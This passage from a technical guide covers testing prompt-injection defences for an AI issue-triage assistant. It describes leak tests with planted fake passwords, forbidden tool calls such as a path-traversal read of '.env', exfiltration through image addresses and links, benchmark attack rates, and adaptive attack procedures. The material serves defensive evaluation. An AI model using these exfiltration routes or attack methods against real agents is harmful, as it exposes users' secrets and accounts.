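A good test also includes a control in which the boundary should fail, because a test that gives the same result with the sandbox on and off isn't testing the sandbox. The software for *CONTINUITY* (2026) includes a deliberate route around the monitor. When that route is open, the forbidden effect occurs even though every check on the normal route still works.

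To find leaks, the tester can put a unique fake password in each private file and search every sink for it, including name lookups, image addresses and saved notes. The search should cover encoded and split copies. Something in the test also has to open the files. *AgentShield* (2026) used fake credentials as alarms, but none went off in its standard tests because the agents never looked at the files. A script that reads the password first avoids this problem.

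### Four tests for the triage assistant

Suppose the assistant runs with the three rules for tool calls, Microsoft's labels, the display rules for images and links, and a sandbox. It also has `run_command` for reproducing crashes, and a rule allows calls to that tool. The tester works on a copy of the repository with a test GitHub account, puts different fake passwords in `.env` and `src/test_key.py`, and refuses every approval request. The task is "Triage issue 412".

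| Test | What the script does | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Forbidden calls | Requests `write_file("build.yml", ...)`, `read_file("src/../.env")` and `post_comment(398, ...)`. Then reads issue 412 and requests two comments on it at the same moment | The monitor refuses the first three calls. Exactly one comment appears under issue 412 |
| A way round the monitor | Runs a program that tries to open `.env`, change `build.yml`, look up a name under the tester's domain and contact GitHub directly | All four attempts fail, and the tester's name server records nothing. With the sandbox off, all four succeed |
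| A marked secret | Reads issue 412 and `src/test_key.py`, then puts the fake password in a comment and in an image address and a link in the final reply | The comment waits for an approval that never comes. The application requests no image and shows the link as plain text |
| A missing label | Removes the label from `read_file` and repeats the marked-secret test | The application refuses to start, or treats the file as private and holds back the comment |

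The last test would fail with the defaults in Microsoft's framework, so the maintainer would have to add a start-up check that every tool has a label.

Software cannot easily detect a label that is present but wrong. If the tester marks `read_file` as public, the monitor enforces the wrong policy and publishes the password from `src/test_key.py`. The password in `.env` stays safe because the path rule and the sandbox both keep the assistant away from that file. Deliberate mistakes like this show the maintainer which secrets are protected by only one setting.

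### Where a proof can replace testing

A tester can try only a limited number of call sequences, but a proof can cover all of them. For example, the maintainer's order rule allows a comment only if the history contains no earlier comment. Let n be the number of comments so far, starting at 0. A permitted call that isn't a comment leaves n unchanged. A permitted comment requires n = 0 and raises it to 1. So n never exceeds 1, however long the run is.

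*Tether* (2026) automates this kind of argument. The developer states a property that the policy should guarantee, and a language model either writes a proof or finds a sequence of calls that violates the property. The proof checker Lean verifies the result and rejects any faulty proof.

Besides its result about the policy, *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* proves that a monitored agent has the same effects as a reference agent that never makes the injected requests. Whenever the monitored agent makes an injected request, the monitor refuses it while the reference agent waits, and the two agents take all other steps together. This proof requires the monitor to be in a refusing state whenever injected text may have influenced the agent, and the paper's proof about the monitor works for any plan.

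These proofs are about a mathematical description of the system. The argument about comments assumes that the monitor checks and records one call at a time, so it doesn't cover two simultaneous requests. The proofs in *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) come closer to the running software, because they cover the interpreter that calls the model. The developer still has to test the network settings, the labels and the tools. A proof can replace tests of the policy's logic only if the running monitor follows the same logic.

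### How AgentDojo scores an attack

Enforcement tests don't show whether the assistant is useful, or how often an attacker gets a misleading comment published through permitted calls. That requires a real model and realistic tasks. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, built the benchmark behind many of the attack rates quoted for agent defences. It pairs every user task with every attacker goal in the same setting:

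| Setting | User tasks | Attacker goals | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 |

In a banking case, the user might ask the agent to pay a bill while hostile text contains instructions to send money elsewhere. After the run, ordinary code checks the simulated accounts. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a model as the judge because an injection that works on the agent might also work on the judge.

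The benchmark produces three figures:

- Utility is the share of the 97 tasks that the agent completes when nobody attacks.
- Utility under attack is the share of the 629 cases in which it completes the user's task and does nothing for the attacker.
- Attack success is the share of the 629 cases in which it carries out the attacker's goal.

An agent that refuses all work scores zero on all three measures. One that pays the user's bill but also sends money to the attacker adds to attack success but not to utility under attack. He et al. define utility under attack differently, requiring only that the user's task succeed, so they count the second agent as useful.

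A low attack success rate can also mean that the agent is too weak to do what the attacker wants. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) explains that AgentDojo therefore lets testers give the agent the attacker's goal as an ordinary request. Narisetty and colleagues ran this check after finding no successful attacks in the office setting, and found that their small model could achieve only three of the six goals when asked directly. AgentDojo has also grown to more than 900 combinations, so two results may come from different versions.

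### What newer benchmarks add

AgentDojo puts hostile text in tool results and evaluates a single session. Testing for poisoned tool descriptions requires a separate benchmark, such as MCPTox. In *ToolFence*, Li and colleagues caution that a good result on one benchmark doesn't show that a defence resists other types of attack.

Several benchmarks test for poisoned memory. MPBench, from *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026), separately measures whether hostile text is saved in one session and whether it influences a later one. *MemPoison* (2026) defines a correct and a poisoned outcome for each later task, and includes text from users, tools and other agents. *MemoryDojo* (November 2026) also tests poisoned memory. A triage assistant that saves notes needs a test of this kind because AgentDojo cannot detect an attack that takes effect in a later session.

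For long tasks, *Blocking at the Boundary* (2026) lists AgentLAB, StepJack, which spreads an attack over a chain of web pages, and ClawTrojan, which plants instructions in an agent's workspace to take effect later. The paper's own benchmark judges single actions instead of whole runs. It compares runs with and without an attack and reports how many harmful actions a defence blocked and how many harmless ones it blocked by mistake.

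In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) object that AgentDojo's outside text contains almost no helpful instructions, which favours defences that suppress outside information. AgentDojo also places some attacks unrealistically. In one case, the hostile text is in the main content of a user's own website, which an attacker normally couldn't edit. AgentDyn instead puts the hostile text in an advertising banner.

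AgentDyn has 60 tasks and 560 security cases in three settings. The GitHub setting, with 20 tasks and 34 tools, is the closest match for the triage assistant. Each task requires replanning and includes at least one helpful instruction from outside. Tasks take 7.1 steps on average, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo. The following results are for GPT-4o, except those for MetaSecAlign, which is itself a model.

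| Defence | Utility without attacks | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| PIGuard | 10.0% | 1.7% |
| Tool filter | 8.3% | 4.2% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| MetaSecAlign | 55.0% | 9.0% |

The low attack rates in the middle rows come from agents that hardly work. The test put systems that rely on approvals at a disadvantage, because the researchers told every agent to finish without asking the user for confirmation. They also used a fixed attack and mostly older models, reasoning that newer models have probably trained on the attack's wording. AgentDyn is therefore better evidence about lost utility than about security.

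### Comparing planning-based and model-based defences

He et al. left planning-based systems such as CaMeL out of their comparison because current benchmarks don't compare them fairly with model-based defences. When the task is "Post a summary of issue 412", a fixed plan rules out injected calls, so the task tests only the model-based defence. When the task is "Fix whatever the issue describes", no fixed plan works, so the planning-based system scores zero for both utility and attack success. The benchmark average therefore depends mostly on the mix of tasks.

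A fair comparison needs tasks in which the agent must use untrusted data to succeed and could also be harmed by it. The scoring code must distinguish using the data from obeying instructions in it. AgentPI, the benchmark by Wang and colleagues, is a step toward this, with five kinds of task that depend on what the agent reads.

An attack's success can also depend on how much the user's request leaves to outside content. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) groups requests this way. "Change my address to 1234 Maple Street" leaves nothing open, "Pay the bill in this file" leaves the amount and recipient open, and "Do everything on my to-do list" leaves even the action open. Against GPT-4o-mini with PIGuard, attacks that adapted to the defence succeeded in 17.3% of the fully specified tasks and 54.2% of those that left the action open. With Progent, the rate was at most 11% in every group,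 partly because its rules often allow only reading in the most open tasks. The triage assistant mostly gets requests that leave something open, so the maintainer should give little weight to results for fully specified ones.

### Running an adaptive test

Testing a defence with fixed attack texts can badly overstate how well it works. PIGuard stopped every fixed attack in the AutoDojo test on GPT-4o-mini, but 28.0% of attacks succeeded after six rounds of revising them. In *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*, Zhan, Fang and colleagues (2025) got past each of the eight defences they tested more than half the time. *The Attacker Moves Second* reports similar results for twelve defences. Wang and colleagues say researchers still test mainly with handwritten templates, although 14 of the 37 attack papers in their review use automated search.

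A developer can run an adaptive test as follows:

1. Write code that detects each forbidden outcome. For the triage assistant, it would search public comments for the fake passwords, compare the files before and after, and look for comments on other issues.
2. Decide where the attacker can write and what the attacker knows. Ma and colleagues' attacker knows the general types of defence but not which one is installed, and learns only whether an attempt succeeded. Narisetty and colleagues' protocol assumes that the attacker also knows the policy, which is the safer assumption if the policy is in a public repository.
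3. Set a budget of rounds, attempts per round and computing cost, and use the same budget for every defence.
4. Fix the stopping rule before starting. A common one is to stop at the first success or at the last permitted round, and to count the whole series as one result.
5. Freeze the application, then let a model or a person revise the text after each round on the basis of the permitted feedback.
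6. Repeat the attacks without the defence, and run ordinary tasks with it.
7. Save every attempt, including the failures.

To save compute, He and colleagues ran adaptive attacks only on cases in which the undefended model was already vulnerable. This is sensible for comparing defences, but the resulting rates don't estimate the risk across all tasks. Defences are hard to compare when the undefended model already resists most attacks. In the AutoDojo test, only 0.3% of the fixed attacks succeeded against the undefended Claude Haiku 4.5, so every defence looked good on it.

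Coding assistants can do some of this work. *Locks Tested Without Burglars*, a 2025 workshop paper, describes how assistants such as Claude Code read the source code of DataSentinel, MELON and DRIFT, found hidden prompts and unstated assumptions, and wrote attacks to match. This raised attack success rates by up to 50–60%. The maintainer can use an assistant in the same way on an isolated copy of the project, and so can an attacker if the code is public. If the assistant finds nothing, that is weak evidence of safety, because models refuse to write some kinds of attack.

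### What later rounds reveal

*Adaptive Adversaries* (Jain, Hartmann and Li, 2026), a benchmark presented at the machine-learning conference ICML, measures how much an attacker gains from further rounds. It has 21 scenarios, such as a reviewer deciding whether to accept a paper. An attacking model writes a text, reads the defending model's answer and tries again, up to 15 times. The defender starts afresh each time. Three models played both roles, and each pairing played five contests in each scenario, for a total of 945.

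| Defending model | Success in the first round | Success within 15 rounds |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0.0% | 7.9% |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.0% | 9.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 1.0% | 16.8% |

An earlier abstract by Jain and colleagues gives success rates of 8.3% to 19.0% for 15 rounds, but the revised paper corrects these figures downwards. Success rates were still rising at the last round, so they would probably have been higher with more rounds.

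The gain came largely from learning. In a separate test on three scenarios, attackers who remembered their earlier attempts won 13 of 36 contests. Attackers without that memory also had 15 tries but won none. Remembering earlier rounds also helped the defender, cutting attack success from 57.4% to 31.5%. An application that opens a new session for every GitHub issue gives up this advantage.

Averages also hid large differences between scenarios. In a scenario about protecting a password, Opus failed in 30 of 60 contests and Gemini in 3. In one about accepting a paper, Opus failed in none of 60 and Gemini in 26. A developer choosing a model should therefore look at the results for the scenarios closest to their application.

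The exact rates shouldn't be applied to other products. The researchers revised the scenarios so that attacks could succeed over several rounds, which partly explains the rise. The defending models only wrote answers and had no real tools, and most pairings had only five contests per scenario. Still, the benchmark shows that testing only the first round can miss most of the attacks a persistent attacker will find.

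### What the numbers can prove

Suppose the triage assistant withstands all 629 attacks in a test. If each attack had an independent chance p of success, the probability of seeing no successes would be (1 − p)⁶²⁹. The highest p that is still compatible with this result at the usual 95% level satisfies

(1 − p)⁶²⁹ = 0.05, so p ≈ 0.48%

If none of the attacks in a test succeed, the 95% upper confidence limit on the attack success rate is approximately 3 divided by the number of attacks. A limit of 0.1% would require about 3,000 attacks without a success.

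Small rates add up when an attacker can keep trying. With a success rate of 0.1% per try, the chance of at least one success in 1,000 independent tries is

1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 63%

If each attempt had a 0.48% chance of success, an attacker who filed 1,000 issues would have a more than 99% chance of succeeding at least once. A defense with that 0.48% failure rate could still score perfectly on 629 cases.

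Both calculations assume that the test cases are independent, which is rarely true in real tests. AgentDojo's 629 cases, for example, reuse 27 attacker goals. If all cases with the same goal had the same result, the test would amount to 27 trials and the upper limit would rise to about 10.5%. The true uncertainty lies between this extreme and full independence.

Repeated tries against one target aren't independent either. The attack on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time on a single try and 63% of the time within a hundred tries. If the tries were independent, the second figure would be more than 99%. It is probably lower because some scenarios resist almost every attempt while others fail within a few tries. However, an attacker who learns from each failure can do better than the formula predicts, as in the contests with and without memory.

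The calculation also applies only to attacks drawn from the same source as the test cases. More trials cannot fix this, because an attacker can choose something the tester never thought of. Before Mellafe Zuvic fixed ScopeGate, a million payments with ordinary amounts could have passed every check, and a payment of NaN would still have got through each time. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) reports no leaks in 15,000 attacks on an application whose code filters the model's replies, so the formula gives an upper limit of 0.02% on the leak rate. But if such a filter searched only for the exact text of a password, an encoded copy would pass every time.

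### What a test report should state

A reader can judge a claim such as "no attack succeeded" only if the report gives these details:

- The exact versions of the model, prompts, tools, policy and benchmark, and the settings of the sandbox.
- Which routes to each sink the monitor covers and which remain open.
- What the attacker could write, knew and learned from each attempt, together with the budget, the number of rounds and the stopping rule.
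- Utility, utility under attack and attack success as counts as well as percentages, with margins of error and definitions.
- The same figures without the defence, and separate figures for different types of task.
- How often the application asked for approval, and how the tester answered. Automatic approval and automatic refusal can give very different results.
- Any runs left out and the reason. Jain and colleagues, for instance, excluded 838 contests from a related competition because the defender's software had failed.

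In that competition, all the defenders used the same model, but attack success differed by 26.5 percentage points depending on the software around it. The model's published attack success rate therefore cannot replace a test of the finished application.

### Logging and retesting after release

After release, the application should record each proposed call, the monitor's decision, the destination and the result, along with the versions of the model, prompts and tool definitions. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) recommends storing these records where the model cannot reach them and new entries never overwrite old ones. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) adds that an agent must be traceable to a responsible person or organisation. The maintainer should keep passwords out of the records and treat any text copied from issues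 as untrusted, particularly if a model will later summarise it.

Decoys can serve as alarms. AgentShield gives the agent a fake tool that no legitimate task needs, so any call to it suggests that the agent is following instructions in hostile text. A fake password in `.env` works similarly if the maintainer gets an alert whenever somebody tries to use it.

| What has changed | What to run again |
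|---|---|
| A rule, label or credential | All enforcement tests, and any proof about the policy |
| A tool or its description | Enforcement tests for that tool, and attack tests on tasks that use it |
| The model, system prompt or a filter | Attack tests and ordinary tasks |
| Nothing, but an alarm or incident has occurred | A new enforcement test that requests the same forbidden action |

The maintainer can run the enforcement tests automatically with every code change because they don't need a model. Attack tests cost more to run, and replaying old attacks is an unreliable way to check whether a problem is fixed. When Jain and colleagues replayed successful attacks, the attacks worked only 67.2% of the time against the same model and 11.8% of the time against other models. The maintainer should therefore replay each old attack several times and then run a new adaptive test, especially after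 switching models.
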